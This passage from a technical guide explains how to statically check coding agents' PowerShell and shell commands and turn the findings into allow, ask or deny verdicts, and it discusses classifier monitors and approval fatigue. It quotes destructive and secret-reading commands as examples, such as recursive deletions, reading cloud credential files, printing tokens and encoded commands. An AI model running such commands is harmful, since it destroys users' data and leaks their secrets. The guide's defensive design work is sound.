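if ($errors.Count -gt 0) { return 'ask' }

$commands = $tree.FindAll({
    $args[0] -is [System.Management.Automation.Language.CommandAst]
}, $true)

foreach ($command in $commands) {
    $name = $command.GetCommandName()
    if (-not $name) { return 'ask' }
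    # Next: resolve the name, bind the parameters, apply the rules
}
```

`ParseInput` returns the tree and stores any syntax errors in `$errors`. `FindAll` then walks the tree and collects the command nodes, in this example, one for `npm` and one for `Remove-Item`. Microsoft (2012) demonstrated the same kind of search when PowerShell 3.0 introduced the syntax tree. PowerShell 2.0 had offered only a flat list of tokens.

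The `$true` at the end of the `FindAll` call extends the search to script blocks, which are pieces of code in braces. Without it, the checker would miss the deletion in `Get-ChildItem | ForEach-Object { Remove-Item $_ }`.

`GetCommandName` returns the command's name, or null if the name can't be determined from the text. Microsoft's *CommandAst Class* gives the example `& $foo`, where the name is in a variable. PowerShell's parser therefore already has a separate result for unknown names, which a Bash checker has to add.

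The checker should use the parser from the PowerShell version that will run the command. Windows includes version 5.1, and developers often install version 7 alongside it. The `||` in our example is a syntax error in 5.1. A command that both versions accept can still behave differently. *PowerPeeler* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) gives the example `'t/e#st'.Split('/#')`, which returns three pieces in version 5 and one in version 7.

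A checker written in another language has to start a PowerShell process to use the parser. Starting one for every command would be slow, so it's better to keep one process running and send it each command.

### Many spellings of one command

The tree preserves the command as the user or agent typed it, and PowerShell accepts many spellings:

| What varies | Example | Standard form |
|---|---|---|
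| Case | `REMOVE-ITEM build` | `Remove-Item -Path build` |
| Alias | `ri build` or `del build` | `Remove-Item -Path build` |
| Abbreviated parameters | `Remove-Item build -r -fo` | `Remove-Item -Path build -Recurse -Force` |
| Positional parameter | `Remove-Item build` | `Remove-Item -Path build` |
| Colon before the value | `Remove-Item -Path:build` | `Remove-Item -Path build` |
| Module-qualified name | `Microsoft.PowerShell.Management\Remove-Item build` | `Remove-Item -Path build` |

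Aliases depend on the platform. According to Microsoft's *Remove-Item*, `rm` is an alias for the `Remove-Item` cmdlet only on Windows. In PowerShell, `rm -rf build` therefore runs the Unix program on Linux but fails on Windows, because `Remove-Item` has no parameter that starts with `rf`.

Users can shorten a parameter to any prefix that distinguishes it from the command's other parameters, as Microsoft's *Using Cmdlet Parameters* (2012) explains. PowerShell Magazine's *#PSTip Argument disambiguation in PowerShell 3.0* (2013) shows that `Get-ChildItem -f` fails because `-f` could mean `-Filter` or `-Force`. `Remove-Item` has the same two parameters, so the shortest valid form of its `-Force` parameter is `-fo`. Valid abbreviations differ between commands, and a new parameter can make an old abbreviation ambiguous.

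Microsoft's *StaticParameterBinder Class* documents a call that applies PowerShell's own parameter-binding algorithm to a command node and returns the bound parameters, so a checker doesn't have to reproduce these rules. For `Remove-Item build -r -fo`, the checker can test for `Path`, `Recurse` and `Force`, however the agent wrote them.

A checker also has to read the values of switches, parameters that are normally either present or absent. `Remove-Item build -Recurse -WhatIf` only reports what it would delete, but with `-WhatIf:$false` the command deletes `build`. A checker that allowed any command containing `-WhatIf` would allow that deletion.

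Some parameters aren't written in the command. In `Start-Process @options`, PowerShell takes them from a table in the variable `$options`, a technique called splatting. If the same line defines the table with constant values, the checker can read them with `SafeGetValue`, which constructs a value from the tree only if that is safe. Otherwise it should treat the parameters as unknown. A session can also have its own default parameter values, according to Microsoft's *about_Parameters*, so the agent should start PowerShell without the user's startup script.

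A standard name can still refer to unexpected code. According to Microsoft, PowerShell looks for an alias first, then a function, then a cmdlet, then an external program. A function called `Remove-Item` therefore takes precedence over the cmdlet. A module-qualified name avoids this, but the checker must also compare the module, because `MyTools\Remove-Item` can do something else.

When a checker looks up an unfamiliar command name, PowerShell may load a module that contains the command, and loading a module can run code. The checker should therefore do its lookups in a session where only trusted modules are available.

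Claude Code handles several of these variations. According to Anthropic, it parses PowerShell's syntax tree, ignores case, and converts common aliases to cmdlet names before matching rules. It also checks each command on the line separately, as it does for Bash.

### Deleting files and other items

`-Recurse` makes `Remove-Item` delete a folder and its contents. Without it, the cmdlet prompts for confirmation before deleting a folder that isn't empty, and Microsoft notes that `-Confirm:$false` doesn't suppress this prompt. `-Force` extends the deletion to hidden and read-only files but doesn't override access permissions. As with `rm`, a checker that flags only commands with both options will miss destructive ones.

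It will also miss deletions that get their targets through a pipe:

```
Get-ChildItem * -Include *.csv -Recurse | Remove-Item
```

This command deletes every CSV file in the current folder and its subfolders, although `Remove-Item` has neither a path nor `-Recurse`. Microsoft's *about_Parameter_Binding* explains that PowerShell binds the arguments in the text first and then tries to fill the remaining parameters from the pipeline. The checker therefore has to take the targets from `Get-ChildItem`. If the checker can't analyse the command before the pipe, the targets are unknown.

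In a recursive deletion, `-Exclude` protects matching items only at the top level. PowerShell deletes matching files in subfolders along with their parent folder, so a checker shouldn't rate the command as safer because it contains `-Exclude`.

The path procedure for Bash needs a few changes for PowerShell. Windows normally ignores case in paths and accepts both forward slashes and backslashes, so the checker has to convert paths to one form before comparing them. It also has to resolve directory junctions, which are Windows links covered in a later section. PowerShell's cmdlets interpret a tilde themselves, even when it is quoted, so `Remove-Item '~' -Recurse` targets the home directory, whereas `rm -r '~'` in Bash targets a folder named `~`.

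An empty variable is as dangerous in PowerShell as in Bash. If `$out` has no value, `Remove-Item "$out\*" -Recurse` deletes the visible contents of the current drive's root. `Set-StrictMode -Version Latest` makes PowerShell report an error if the variable was never set, but it doesn't catch a variable set to an empty string.

`Remove-Item` isn't limited to files. PowerShell presents several other kinds of data as drives, and the same cmdlet works on them:

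| Command | What it deletes |
|---|---|
| `Remove-Item build -Recurse` | A folder |
| `Remove-Item HKLM:\Software\MyCompany\OldApp -Recurse` | Settings in the Windows registry, for all users |
| `Remove-Item Env:\CC` | An environment variable in the current process |
| `Remove-Item Alias:\show` | An alias in the current session |

`Remove-Item` can also delete a certificate, and with `-DeleteKey` it deletes the private key too. Deleting a private key or a registry key can break other programs, while deleting an alias rarely matters. The checker therefore has to identify the drive before it rates the risk of deleting the target. It also has to follow `Set-Location`, PowerShell's version of `cd`. After `Set-Location HKLM:\Software\MyCompany`, the path `OldApp` refers to a registry key even though it looks like a folder.

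Single registry values need another rule because a different cmdlet, `Remove-ItemProperty`, deletes them.

### Starting an elevated process

On Windows, even an administrator's programs usually run with ordinary rights. A running process can't raise its own rights, so it has to start a new process and request elevation. By default, Windows then asks the user to approve the request in a User Account Control window.

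In PowerShell, `Start-Process` with `-Verb RunAs` requests administrator privileges for the program it starts. A checker should examine the value bound to `-Verb` instead of searching the text for "RunAs", which can also match other options. Microsoft's *Start-Process* lists `-RunAs` as an alias for `-Credential`, which runs a program under a specified account, and `RunAsUser` as a separate verb. The cmdlet also has the aliases `saps` and, on Windows, `start`.

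If the developer started the agent's terminal as administrator, every command already runs with full rights and no such request appears in the text. The checker should therefore find out whether the shell that will run the command is elevated.

The command that an elevated process runs is often inside a string. Brundage (2009), in *V2 Quick Tip*, published this line on Microsoft's PowerShell blog:

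```
Start-Process "$psHome\powershell.exe" -Verb Runas -ArgumentList '-command "Get-Process"'
```

The first parse finds one command node, `Start-Process`. Binding its parameters gives:

| Parameter | Value |
|---|---|
| `FilePath` | `"$psHome\powershell.exe"` |
| `Verb` | `Runas` |
| `ArgumentList` | `-command "Get-Process"` |

To the outer shell, the last value is ordinary text. To find out what will run with administrator rights, the checker has to continue:

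1. Replace `$psHome` with PowerShell's installation folder. PowerShell sets this variable itself and doesn't let commands change it. In version 7 the program is called `pwsh.exe`, so the line works only in Windows PowerShell.
2. Recognise that the program is another PowerShell.
3. Split the argument string as the new process will, which gives `-command` and `Get-Process`.
4. Parse `Get-Process` as a new PowerShell command and apply the rules to it.
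5. Record that it will run with administrator rights.

`Get-Process` only lists running programs, so the inner command is harmless. But if the string contained `Remove-Item C:\Data -Recurse`, the outer command would have the same name and verb. A checker that stopped after the first parse couldn't distinguish the two. The User Account Control window wouldn't help much either, because it identifies the program as Windows PowerShell.

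The example runs the user's profile as well as `Get-Process`, because PowerShell runs this startup script unless the command includes `-NoProfile`. The profile is normally in a folder that the user's ordinary programs can change, so an agent could have edited it earlier. The checker should analyse the profile or prompt the agent to add `-NoProfile`.

`-ArgumentList` also accepts an array of strings, which `Start-Process` joins with spaces. An element such as `C:\Old Data` becomes two arguments unless it contains its own quotes, so the checker must join the array before parsing it. If the new process is `cmd.exe`, the older Windows command prompt, the string is in another language with its own quoting and variables, and a checker without a parser for that language should ask the user to approve the command.

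### Credentials, environment variables and the registry

Many of the credential files described in the previous section have the same names on Windows, under the user's profile folder. PowerShell's command history file, `ConsoleHost_history.txt`, can also contain passwords that users typed.

PowerShell exposes environment variables through a drive, which makes them easy to read by accident. `Get-ChildItem Env:` prints all of them, including any access tokens, using the same cmdlet that lists files. An allow rule for `Get-ChildItem` should therefore apply only to file drives.

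A line can also reveal a token without containing a command:

```
$env:GITHUB_TOKEN
```

PowerShell prints the value of any expression that stands alone. If that expression is just a variable, the tree has a variable node but no command node, so the loop at the start of this section would have nothing to check. The checker has to examine variables too, and fail closed on any node type it doesn't handle.

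Reading the registry can also expose credentials, because Windows can store the password for automatic sign-in there as plain text, and some programs save their own passwords there. Writing to it can have lasting effects, because Windows starts the programs listed under certain `Run` keys whenever the user signs in. As with file access, the checker therefore needs a list of sensitive locations and has to distinguish reads from writes.

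Saved secrets may also have dedicated commands for reading them. `Get-Secret`, from Microsoft's SecretManagement module, retrieves a stored secret, and with `-AsPlainText` it returns a string that PowerShell prints. `Get-Credential` has a similar name but asks the user to enter a name and password.

On Windows, even reading a file can leak credentials if the file is on another computer. A path such as `\\server\share\file` makes Windows contact that server, and Windows may send the user's credentials to it. Anthropic says this is why Claude Code, in manual mode, prompts the user before running otherwise read-only Bash and PowerShell commands that contain such a path.

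### Names and code computed at run time

The call operator, `&`, runs a command whose name is in a string or variable:

```
$c = "Get-Process"; & $c
```

`GetCommandName` returns null for the second command. As in Bash, the checker can substitute the value if the variable is a constant.

The call operator treats the whole string as a command name and, unlike Bash, doesn't split it at spaces. If `$c` contained `Get-Service -Name Spooler`, PowerShell would look for a command with that entire name and report an error, as Microsoft shows.

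`Invoke-Expression`, or `iex`, is PowerShell's equivalent of `eval`. It parses a string as code, so `Invoke-Expression "1+1"` returns 2, while `& "1+1"` fails. `GetCommandName` returns `Invoke-Expression` for the first command, so a test for missing names won't catch that call. The checker needs a separate rule that parses the string if it is constant and otherwise treats the code as unknown.

A dot followed by a space runs a script in the current scope, as in `. .\setup.ps1`. As with `eval` in Bash, the script can change what names in the rest of the line refer to, so the checker cannot reliably resolve them unless it analyses the script.

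Code can also reach a new PowerShell process in several ways. Microsoft's *about_Pwsh* documents the main ones for version 7:

| Option | Where the code comes from | What the checker can do |
|---|---|---|
| `-Command` or `-c` | The rest of the command line | Parse it again |
| `-File` or `-f` | A script file | Read and parse the file |
| `-EncodedCommand`, `-ec` or `-e` | Encoded text | Decode it, then parse it |
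| `-Command -` or `-File -` | Standard input | Analyse the command before the pipe |

A checker can still read a constant command that has been encoded. For example, `pwsh -e RwBlAHQALQBEAGEAdABlAA==` runs `Get-Date`. The argument is base64-encoded UTF-16LE text, which uses two bytes for each of these characters. A checker that decoded the bytes as UTF-8 would get a zero byte after every character and fail to recognise `Get-Date`.

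Encoding alone is weak evidence of an attack because it is a normal way to avoid problems with nested quotes. Splunk warns that *Malicious PowerShell Process*, its detection rule for encoded commands, can produce false positives from administrators and legitimate scripts. A checker that decodes the command can analyze its contents and needs to prompt the user only if the encoded text comes from an unknown value.

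### Why .NET calls escape cmdlet rules

PowerShell code can call the methods of .NET classes directly:

```
[System.IO.Directory]::Delete('C:\Data', $true)
```

This deletes the folder and everything in it, but the syntax tree contains a method call and no command node, so rules for `Remove-Item` don't apply. Method calls can also download files. *PowerDrive* (Ugarte, Maiorca and colleagues, 2019) describes a typical malicious script in which the cmdlet `New-Object` creates a web client, whose `DownloadFile` method then fetches a program. A rule that covers only the download cmdlet `Invoke-WebRequest` would miss this download.

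Methods can also follow a harmless cmdlet. `Get-Process notepad` displays information about the text editor, but `(Get-Process notepad).Kill()` closes it. A checker that looked only at command nodes would classify both as reads.

It is safer to allow a short list of .NET members, such as `[datetime]::Now` and the mathematical functions in `[Math]`, and ask the user about everything else. Listing the dangerous methods instead isn't practical because .NET has thousands of classes and users can add more. The text of a call such as `$item.Delete()` also doesn't show which class the method belongs to. Microsoft adds that a member's name may be an expression, so a method's name, like a command's, may be unknown until the code runs.

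Relative paths need separate treatment, too. `Set-Location` changes PowerShell's location but not the process's working directory, which .NET methods use. If PowerShell starts in `C:\site`, the following line deletes `C:\site\log.txt`, not the file in `build`:

```
Set-Location build; [System.IO.File]::Delete('log.txt')
```

A checker that applied the rules for cmdlet paths would examine the wrong file.

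### What malware research has found

Most research on analysing PowerShell concerns malware. Attackers often use PowerShell because Windows includes it, and they disguise their scripts to avoid detection.

Early studies tried to classify scripts from their text or syntax. *POSTER* (Rusak, Al-Dujaili and O'Reilly, 2018) describes two. In 2017, Bohannon and Holmes first compared character frequencies in disguised and ordinary scripts, then used 4,098 features of the syntax tree, such as the frequency of each node type. Their classifier was meant to detect disguise rather than harm. In 2018, Hendler and colleagues trained neural networks on the text of 6,290 malicious and 60,098 harmless commands. The networks reached an AUC between 0.985 and 0.990, where 1 means that a classifier ranks every malicious command above every harmless one. False positives rose on a held-out test set.

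Rusak and colleagues used syntax trees to sort 4,079 malicious scripts into families. A classifier given only the tree's depth and number of nodes identified a script's family with 85% accuracy among the eight largest families. This shows that scripts in one family often share a structure, perhaps because attackers reuse templates. Since every script was malicious, the experiment didn't test whether tree size can separate harmful commands from harmless ones.

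Other researchers tried to recover the original script. Ugarte and colleagues built PowerDrive, which removes one layer of obfuscation at a time. It uses text patterns to reassemble split strings. For encoded or compressed layers, it defines a function called `Invoke-Expression` that prints its argument. When a function and a cmdlet share a name, PowerShell runs the function, so the script's decoded text is printed for PowerDrive instead of being run. PowerDrive repeats this until it finds no more layers, then runs the result to collect any further downloads. Ugarte and colleagues report that it accurately analysed more than 95% of the scripts in a collection of thousands.

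The method doesn't cover strings that a script computes without `Invoke-Expression`. Li and colleagues describe a script that stores a web address as encoded bytes and decodes them in a loop. A static tool has to simulate the loop and track every variable, which existing tools did poorly.

Li and colleagues' own tool, PowerPeeler, is a modified version of PowerShell 7 that monitors a script as it runs. It links each expression in the syntax tree to the instructions that PowerShell generates from it, records the results, and writes them back into the script. Li and colleagues tested PowerPeeler on 4,264 script files and 381 command lines selected from 1.7 million malicious samples. Its results were correct 95% of the time, compared with 46% for the next-best tool.

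Language models can read such scripts without running them. *SCRIPTIOC-BENCH* (Kim, Cui and colleagues, 2026) asked models to extract web addresses, domains, IP addresses and file paths from 634 malicious scripts, 75 of them in PowerShell. The best model reached an F1 score of 65.4. The strongest models found up to 91.7% of the items that appeared directly in the text, but only 31% to 46% of those that required following the script's logic. The models were also less reliable on longer scripts.

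These results combine three scripting languages and concern malware, so they don't measure how well a model would review an agent's commands. They suggest that a checker shouldn't rely on a model to work out what encoded text contains. Decoding base64 first takes little compute and gives an exact result. If the decoded text still depends on a loop or an unknown variable, the model's answer may be wrong.

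### Malware and an agent's mistakes

Malware detectors look for signs of an attacker, but many harmful agent commands have none. For example, `Remove-Item C:\Users\ana -Recurse -Force` is short and undisguised, and it uses an ordinary cmdlet and parameters. Its syntax tree is nearly the same as that of a command that deletes a build folder, and a classifier trained on malware is unlikely to learn which paths are safe to delete.

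Malware analysis and command checking also allow different methods. An analyst can run a suspicious script on an isolated machine, and PowerPeeler's tests allowed two minutes per sample. A checker has to decide before the command runs, usually within a fraction of a second. However, it can return a disguised command to the agent and request a plain version, while an analyst has to work with whatever the attacker wrote.

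Malware research is still useful when an attacker has planted instructions for the agent, because the resulting command may contain the same downloads and encodings as ordinary malware. A checker can reuse decoding methods from that research and treat heavy obfuscation as a reason to ask for approval.

### Checks while PowerShell is running

Windows can also inspect code that the static checker couldn't read. The Antimalware Scan Interface, or AMSI, lets PowerShell send each script block to the computer's antivirus program before running it. If a command passes downloaded text to `Invoke-Expression`, AMSI receives the text itself rather than only the variable or address available to the static checker.

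Li and colleagues explain that PowerShell passes script blocks to AMSI as written, without the results of expressions inside them. If a block joins two strings, the antivirus program receives the two parts but not the joined string. The antivirus program also looks for malware, so it isn't designed to stop an ordinary `Remove-Item` command aimed at the wrong folder.

PowerShell's constrained language mode allows cmdlets but restricts scripts to a short list of approved .NET types. It would reject the call to `System.IO.Directory` above, while `Remove-Item` would still work. A checker's rules for cmdlets therefore cover more of what a command can do. Administrators should enforce the mode through Windows application control, because a setting inside the session isn't a reliable security boundary. Some legitimate scripts stop working in this mode. It also doesn't restrict external programs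 that Windows allows to run, so a Python script, for example, can still delete any file that the user can.

PowerShell's execution policy determines which script files PowerShell will run, but a command can usually change it for a new process with `-ExecutionPolicy`. So a checker shouldn't treat a strict policy as a reason to allow a command.

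## Turning findings into allow, ask or deny

Once a checker has worked out which programs a command will run, which paths they touch and what remains unknown, it has to reduce these findings to one verdict. It can check the command against a denylist of what may never run, check it against an allowlist of what may run without asking, or add up the evidence as a score. Coding agents mostly use lists. *One Goal, Many Commands* (Chen and Lin, 2026) describes the usual arrangement, in which the agent refuses anything on the denylist, runs anything on the allowlist, and passes the rest to a person or a second model.

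### Denylists

A denylist rule against `rm -rf ~` is quick to write and will hardly ever interrupt normal work, but a denylist has no effect on commands that its author didn't think of, and Unix has many ways to read, overwrite or delete a file. Chen and Lin tested 1,709 denylists from projects on GitHub. They found that, depending on the file operation, 69.0% to 98.6% of the lists that targeted it failed to block it fully, and that a list aimed at file reading would need 217 more commands on average.

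Administrators had this problem long before coding agents existed. In `/etc/sudoers`, they can allow a user to run every command and then exclude some with an exclamation mark. CentOS, a Linux distribution, has published a version of the file's manual with a warning that allowing "all but a few" commands this way "rarely works as intended".

Denylists work better when a rule names an effect instead of a program. A rule against writing to `/etc/sudoers` covers every program whose file arguments the checker understands. For programs it doesn't understand, the checker can return `ask`, a fallback that a list of text patterns doesn't have.

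### Allowlists

With an allowlist, a command mistakenly left off the list triggers a prompt instead of running and possibly doing damage. The drawback is more prompts, as Li found when comparing Codex with the more permissive OpenCode.

A good allow rule specifies an operation, not just a program. OpenAI (2026) gives two examples from its own use of Codex. One allows `gh pr view` and `gh pr list`, which display proposed code changes on GitHub. The other allows `kubectl`, a tool for managing clusters of servers, but only with the subcommands `get`, `describe` and `logs`. Each rule includes a written justification so that later reviewers can tell why it exists.

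Users often write much broader rules. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), 49.5% of active users of the terminal version had written an allow rule for Bash by June 2026. Five percent allowed any shell command, and another 43% had rules such as `python:*`, which allows any Python program and is therefore nearly as broad. Claude Code ignores these rules in automatic mode.

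Prompts encourage broad rules because clicking "Always Allow" is the quickest way to stop them. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) reports a study of 16 people, 13 of whom said they used this button simply to dismiss prompts. Only three read prompts carefully. Participants granted limited-scope permissions 3.5 times as often with ConLeash, the paper's proposed authorisation system, as with the baseline. A checker's prompt should therefore offer a narrow rule, such as one for this command in this directory, as prominently as the broad one.

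### When rules conflict

Suppose a project has three rules, in this order:

```
deny   git push --force
ask    git push
allow  git
```

`git push --force` can overwrite the history on the server, and it matches all three rules. The verdict depends on how the checker resolves the conflict:

| Command | Strictest rule applies | Last matching rule applies |
|---|---|---|
| `git push --force` | Deny | Allow |
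| `git push` | Ask | Allow |
| `git status` | Allow | Allow |

`sudo` uses the method in the last column. Gratisoft's *Sudoers Manual* specifies that the last matching rule applies, even if an earlier one is more specific. Anyone who adds a general allow rule at the bottom of the file can therefore cancel an earlier ban without noticing.

A checker is safer when the strictest matching rule applies, as in Codex, because the order of the rules then doesn't matter. In Claude Code, deny rules hold in every mode, even the one that skips nearly all prompts. Anthropic also says that no allow rule can approve an `rm` command that Claude Code recognises as removing a critical path.

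The drawback is that an allow rule can't make an exception to a deny rule. If a project's rules deny `rm -r` and allow `rm -r build`, the allow rule never has any effect. Whoever writes the rules has to narrow the deny rule instead, for example to targets outside the project's build output.

Who wrote a rule also matters. In OpenAI's Codex, administrators can set requirements that users can't override. Rules stored in the project need more caution, since the agent or an attacker may be able to edit them. A checker can safely accept deny rules from project files, but it should accept allow rules only from a place the agent can't write to.

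### CARE's score

A list reaches its verdict from a single match, while a score can combine several weak signs. CARE gives each command four scores between 0 and 1 and adds them like this:

score = 0.3 × semantic + 0.3 × path + 0.3 × pattern + 0.1 × structure

The program's class sets the starting semantic score, which is 0 for read-only programs such as `cat` and 1 for destructive ones such as `mkfs`, and risky options raise it. The path score is the score of the riskiest path. Liu and colleagues base the pattern score on the strongest matching pattern and weight it by the pattern's source: 1.00 for MITRE ATT&CK, 0.85 for GTFOBins (a public catalogue of Unix programs that attackers can misuse) and 0.60 for patterns they wrote themselves. The structure score ranges from 0.05 for an ordinary pipe to 1.00 for a pipe into an interpreter.

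CARE allows a command with a total below 0.15 and denies one with 0.35 or more. Anything between gets a WARN, or "ask". Three commands from earlier sections show how this works:

| Command | Calculation | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| `cat /etc/os-release` | 0.3 × 0.10 (path) = 0.03 | Allow |
| `rsync -avz ./build/ admin@gpu01:/data/` | 0.3 × 0.40 (semantic) + 0.3 × 0.75 (pattern) = 0.345 | Ask |
| `cat ~/.aws/credentials` | 0.3 × 0.85 (path) = 0.255 | Ask by the score, but a separate rule on secret files denies it |

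The `rsync` command gets its pattern score because it matches a pattern for transfers between machines.

### What the total hides

The harmless deployment has a higher total than the command that prints the keys to a cloud account, so any threshold low enough to deny that command would also deny the deployment.

The weights cause this. A single score contributes at most 0.30, which is below the 0.35 needed for a refusal, so a decisive fact that raises only one score can't trigger a refusal. Related evidence, however, counts several times. In an example from Liu and colleagues, a disguised `rm -rf /var/log/*` gets 0.95 for its meaning, 1.00 for its path and 1.00 for its pattern, although all three scores largely reflect the same fact.

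Liu and colleagues compensate with three rules that turn a WARN into a refusal. Two are the rules for sensitive paths and high-risk programs described earlier, and the third applies to strong matches with a pattern from a public catalogue. On their main test, these rules decided 94 of the 117 commands that got a WARN. In the uncertain range, the sum therefore mostly served to select commands for the rules to decide.

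A total can also depend heavily on one default value, such as the 0.105 that CARE adds for an unlisted program. When Liu and colleagues lowered the WARN threshold to 0.10 in the version without a language model, detection rose from 76% to 97%, but false positives rose from 2% to 23%. Doubling the semantic weight instead gave the same two rates. Either change would have put unlisted programs over the threshold, which probably explains the results.

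Giving each finding its own verdict and applying the strictest is simpler than combining findings into a score. The checker can then report which finding determined the result, and a project's owner can change one rule without affecting the results for unrelated commands. A score is still useful for findings too weak to justify a prompt on their own.

### When a person answers

An "ask" verdict protects the user only if whoever answers can tell a harmful command from a harmless one. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accept 93% of permission prompts, and by August 2026 Anthropic put the figure at 97%. Even careful users would accept most prompts, since most proposed commands are harmless. But the users who accept nearly all these prompts reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, so they do object when a request gives them something substantial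 to evaluate.

Anthropic also reports an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, who did coding tasks without being told which behaviour was under study. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it, while the model that reviews actions in automatic mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

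The testers weren't working on their own projects and had little to lose, so developers at work may do better than 13.6%. Anthropic also published the result to explain why it was making automatic mode the default. The decline within sessions is harder to dismiss, because the setting was equally artificial throughout. A likely cause is approval fatigue, the tendency to pay less attention after many prompts.

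Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) surveyed 203 users of coding agents for *From Delegation to Action Approval*. Even among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the generated code, 61% often approved at least one type of action without close review. Developers who knew of security or privacy incidents did so more often than others, which suggests that warning developers about past incidents won't solve the problem.

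Many prompts also contain too little information for a good decision. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most production prompts consist of the raw command on a single line. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine, but approving it authorises whatever the script contains. User review contributed to 105 of the paper's 290 reports. In 80 of them the user had approved actions automatically, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative.

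A checker can help by asking less often and by describing what a command would do instead of repeating it. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) suggests that prompts should also show whether the user could recover from the action. If nobody is available to answer, "ask" has to become "deny". Claude Code has a mode for automated scripts that does this.

### When a second model answers

A second model can review actions without fatigue and take the user's request into account. In Claude Code's automatic mode, this model is a classifier that reviews the actions simpler rules leave undecided. Claude Code can read files and edit those inside the project without this review.

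The classifier works in two steps. It first gives a quick yes-or-no answer that leans towards blocking, and it reasons at length only about actions that this answer would block. Anthropic measured both steps:

| | First step only | Both steps |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions blocked, in 10,000 real tool calls | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Harmful actions missed, in 52 real cases where the agent had gone too far | 6.6% | 17% |

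The second step removes nearly all false alarms but lets more harmful actions through. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly treated the action as one the user had agreed to. Asking an agent to clean up a pull request, for instance, doesn't authorise a forced push.

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's proposed actions. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations because they might persuade the classifier to approve something harmful, and removes tool output because an attacker could plant instructions there. CARE's language model receives the command, its score and the patterns it matched, but not the user's request, so it can't tell whether the user wanted a deletion. It is instructed to refuse when uncertain.

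CARE's results show why a model shouldn't be able to overrule strong static evidence. On the main test, its model correctly released three `rsync` commands. But on 600 attack commands written by the same model, 52.5% passed the check and ran successfully, compared with 37.3% when CARE blocked every WARN without consulting the model. Liu and colleagues suspect that the model approved attacks because it had written them. Claude Code's classifier is never supposed to approve certain actions, including sending code or secrets to outside parties, even if the user asks for them in the session.

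Static findings can also improve the model's answer. Before a command such as `git reset --hard`, Claude Code gives the classifier the repository's current Git status, so the model can consider which uncommitted changes the command would discard.

### Telling the model where the boundary is

A rule against "destructive commands" leaves the model to decide what counts as destructive. *Decision Models as Policy Gates for Coding Agents* (Beno, 2026) tested whether more explicit rules help. The study used two general language models and 22 decision models, which output probabilities for fixed questions instead of generating text.

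GPT-6 wrote 2,643 fictional tool calls, including shell commands, file edits and messages. Some looked dangerous but were harmless, such as a dry run or a deletion command quoted in a note. Claude Opus 5.5 then labelled every call against 28 rules without seeing GPT-6's labels, and the two models agreed on 99.9% of them. Beno reserved 1,108 calls for the final test, from scenarios that didn't appear in the development set.

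Each model judged the calls under two versions of the rules. The short version defined each rule in one sentence, and the long version added examples and counterexamples. For the rule about discarding uncommitted changes, the examples include `git reset --hard` and `git clean -f`, and the counterexamples include `git reset --soft` and `git clean -n`. A model wrote these lists without access to the test cases.

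Here are the results for Jev 1.14, one of the strongest models, on the 23 rules that identify risky actions:

| | Definitions only | With examples and counterexamples |
|---|---|---|
| Hazards detected | 89.3% | 98.2% |
| False positives per rule | 2.49% | 0.83% |
| Harmless actions interrupted | 30.6% | 4.8% |

Detection improved for all 23 models that completed both versions, by 5.5 to 26.1 percentage points, and false positives fell for 21 of them. In a smaller test with 16 new scenarios, detection improved for 22 models.

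Users notice what the last row of the table measures. If each of 23 rules has a false-positive rate of 2.49% and the errors are independent, about 44% of harmless actions will trigger at least one rule. The measured figure was lower, at nearly one harmless action in three, which suggests that false alarms tend to fall on the same actions. Anyone who adds a rule to a checker should therefore measure interruptions per command as well as errors per rule.

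When Beno replaced the names of commands and options in the examples with general descriptions, detection on the ten strongest models changed by at most half a point, although six weaker ones lost between 2 and 10 points. The strong models apparently recognised the commands already and used the examples to determine what the policy allowed, not just as a list of strings to match.

Some of the improvement comes from the study's design, because the labels follow the detailed boundaries and a model given only the short definition may have been marked wrong for a defensible answer. The calls were also synthetic, the study doesn't establish how well the models withstand deliberate attacks, and Beno works for Agent Approve, which makes a policy engine of this kind. The practical advice still holds, because a team that wants its own boundary enforced has to state it.

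Jev typically answered in 120 milliseconds and cost $0.46 per thousand requests, so a checker could reasonably consult such a model about every command its lists leave undecided. But it must send the whole command, because 19 of 21 models detected fewer hazards when Beno cut 20 very long actions to their first 16 kilobytes. If a command is too long for the model, the checker should ask a person.

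### The verdict on the running example

The running example once more:

```
cd build && sudo timeout 30 rm -rf "$OUT"/* > log.txt; git status
```

Assuming that `build` is an ordinary directory in the project and part of the same Git repository, the findings lead to these verdicts:

| Part | Finding | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| `cd build` | Enters a directory in the project | Allow |
| `sudo timeout 30 rm -rf "$OUT"/*` | Deletes files as root; the target is unknown and could be the top of the file system | Ask |
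| `> log.txt` | Creates or empties a log file in `build` | Allow |
| `git status` | Lists changed files | Allow |

The strictest verdict applies, so the answer for the whole line is "ask". Nothing in the text proves that the deletion is harmful, because `OUT` may well contain the path of a temporary directory. But a person who gets the prompt probably won't know the value of `OUT` either, and neither will a second model. The checker can save them the trouble by first returning the command to the agent:

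```
Not run. The target of rm depends on OUT, and this command doesn't set OUT.
If OUT is empty, the command deletes every top-level directory.
Write the target as a literal path inside the project.
Use sudo only if the files belong to root, and explain why.
Don't delete the files in another way.
```

The reason has to be complete. By its published values, CARE would refuse this line because of `sudo`, whatever `OUT` contained. An agent that learned only that `sudo` was the problem could remove it and try again, and the new command might still delete all of the user's files. The message includes its last line because agents normally try another way to do the task after a refusal. *Let the Agent Do It?* points out that these further attempts can feel like overreach when the user objected to the purpose of an action rather than the particular command.

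If the agent insists on the original command, the user should see a prompt like this:

```
Delete the contents of an unknown directory as administrator?

Target:    "$OUT"/*   (the value of OUT is unknown)
Worst case: OUT is empty, and every top-level directory is deleted
Recovery:  only from a backup
Also:      empties build/log.txt if it exists

[Don't run]   [Run once]
```

The prompt has no "Always Allow" button, because `OUT` could have a different value next time. In most cases the user won't see the prompt. If the files are build output, the agent can write `rm -r build/out`, and the checker can allow that without asking, provided the project's owner has listed the directory as safe to delete.

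## Why a static check cannot be complete

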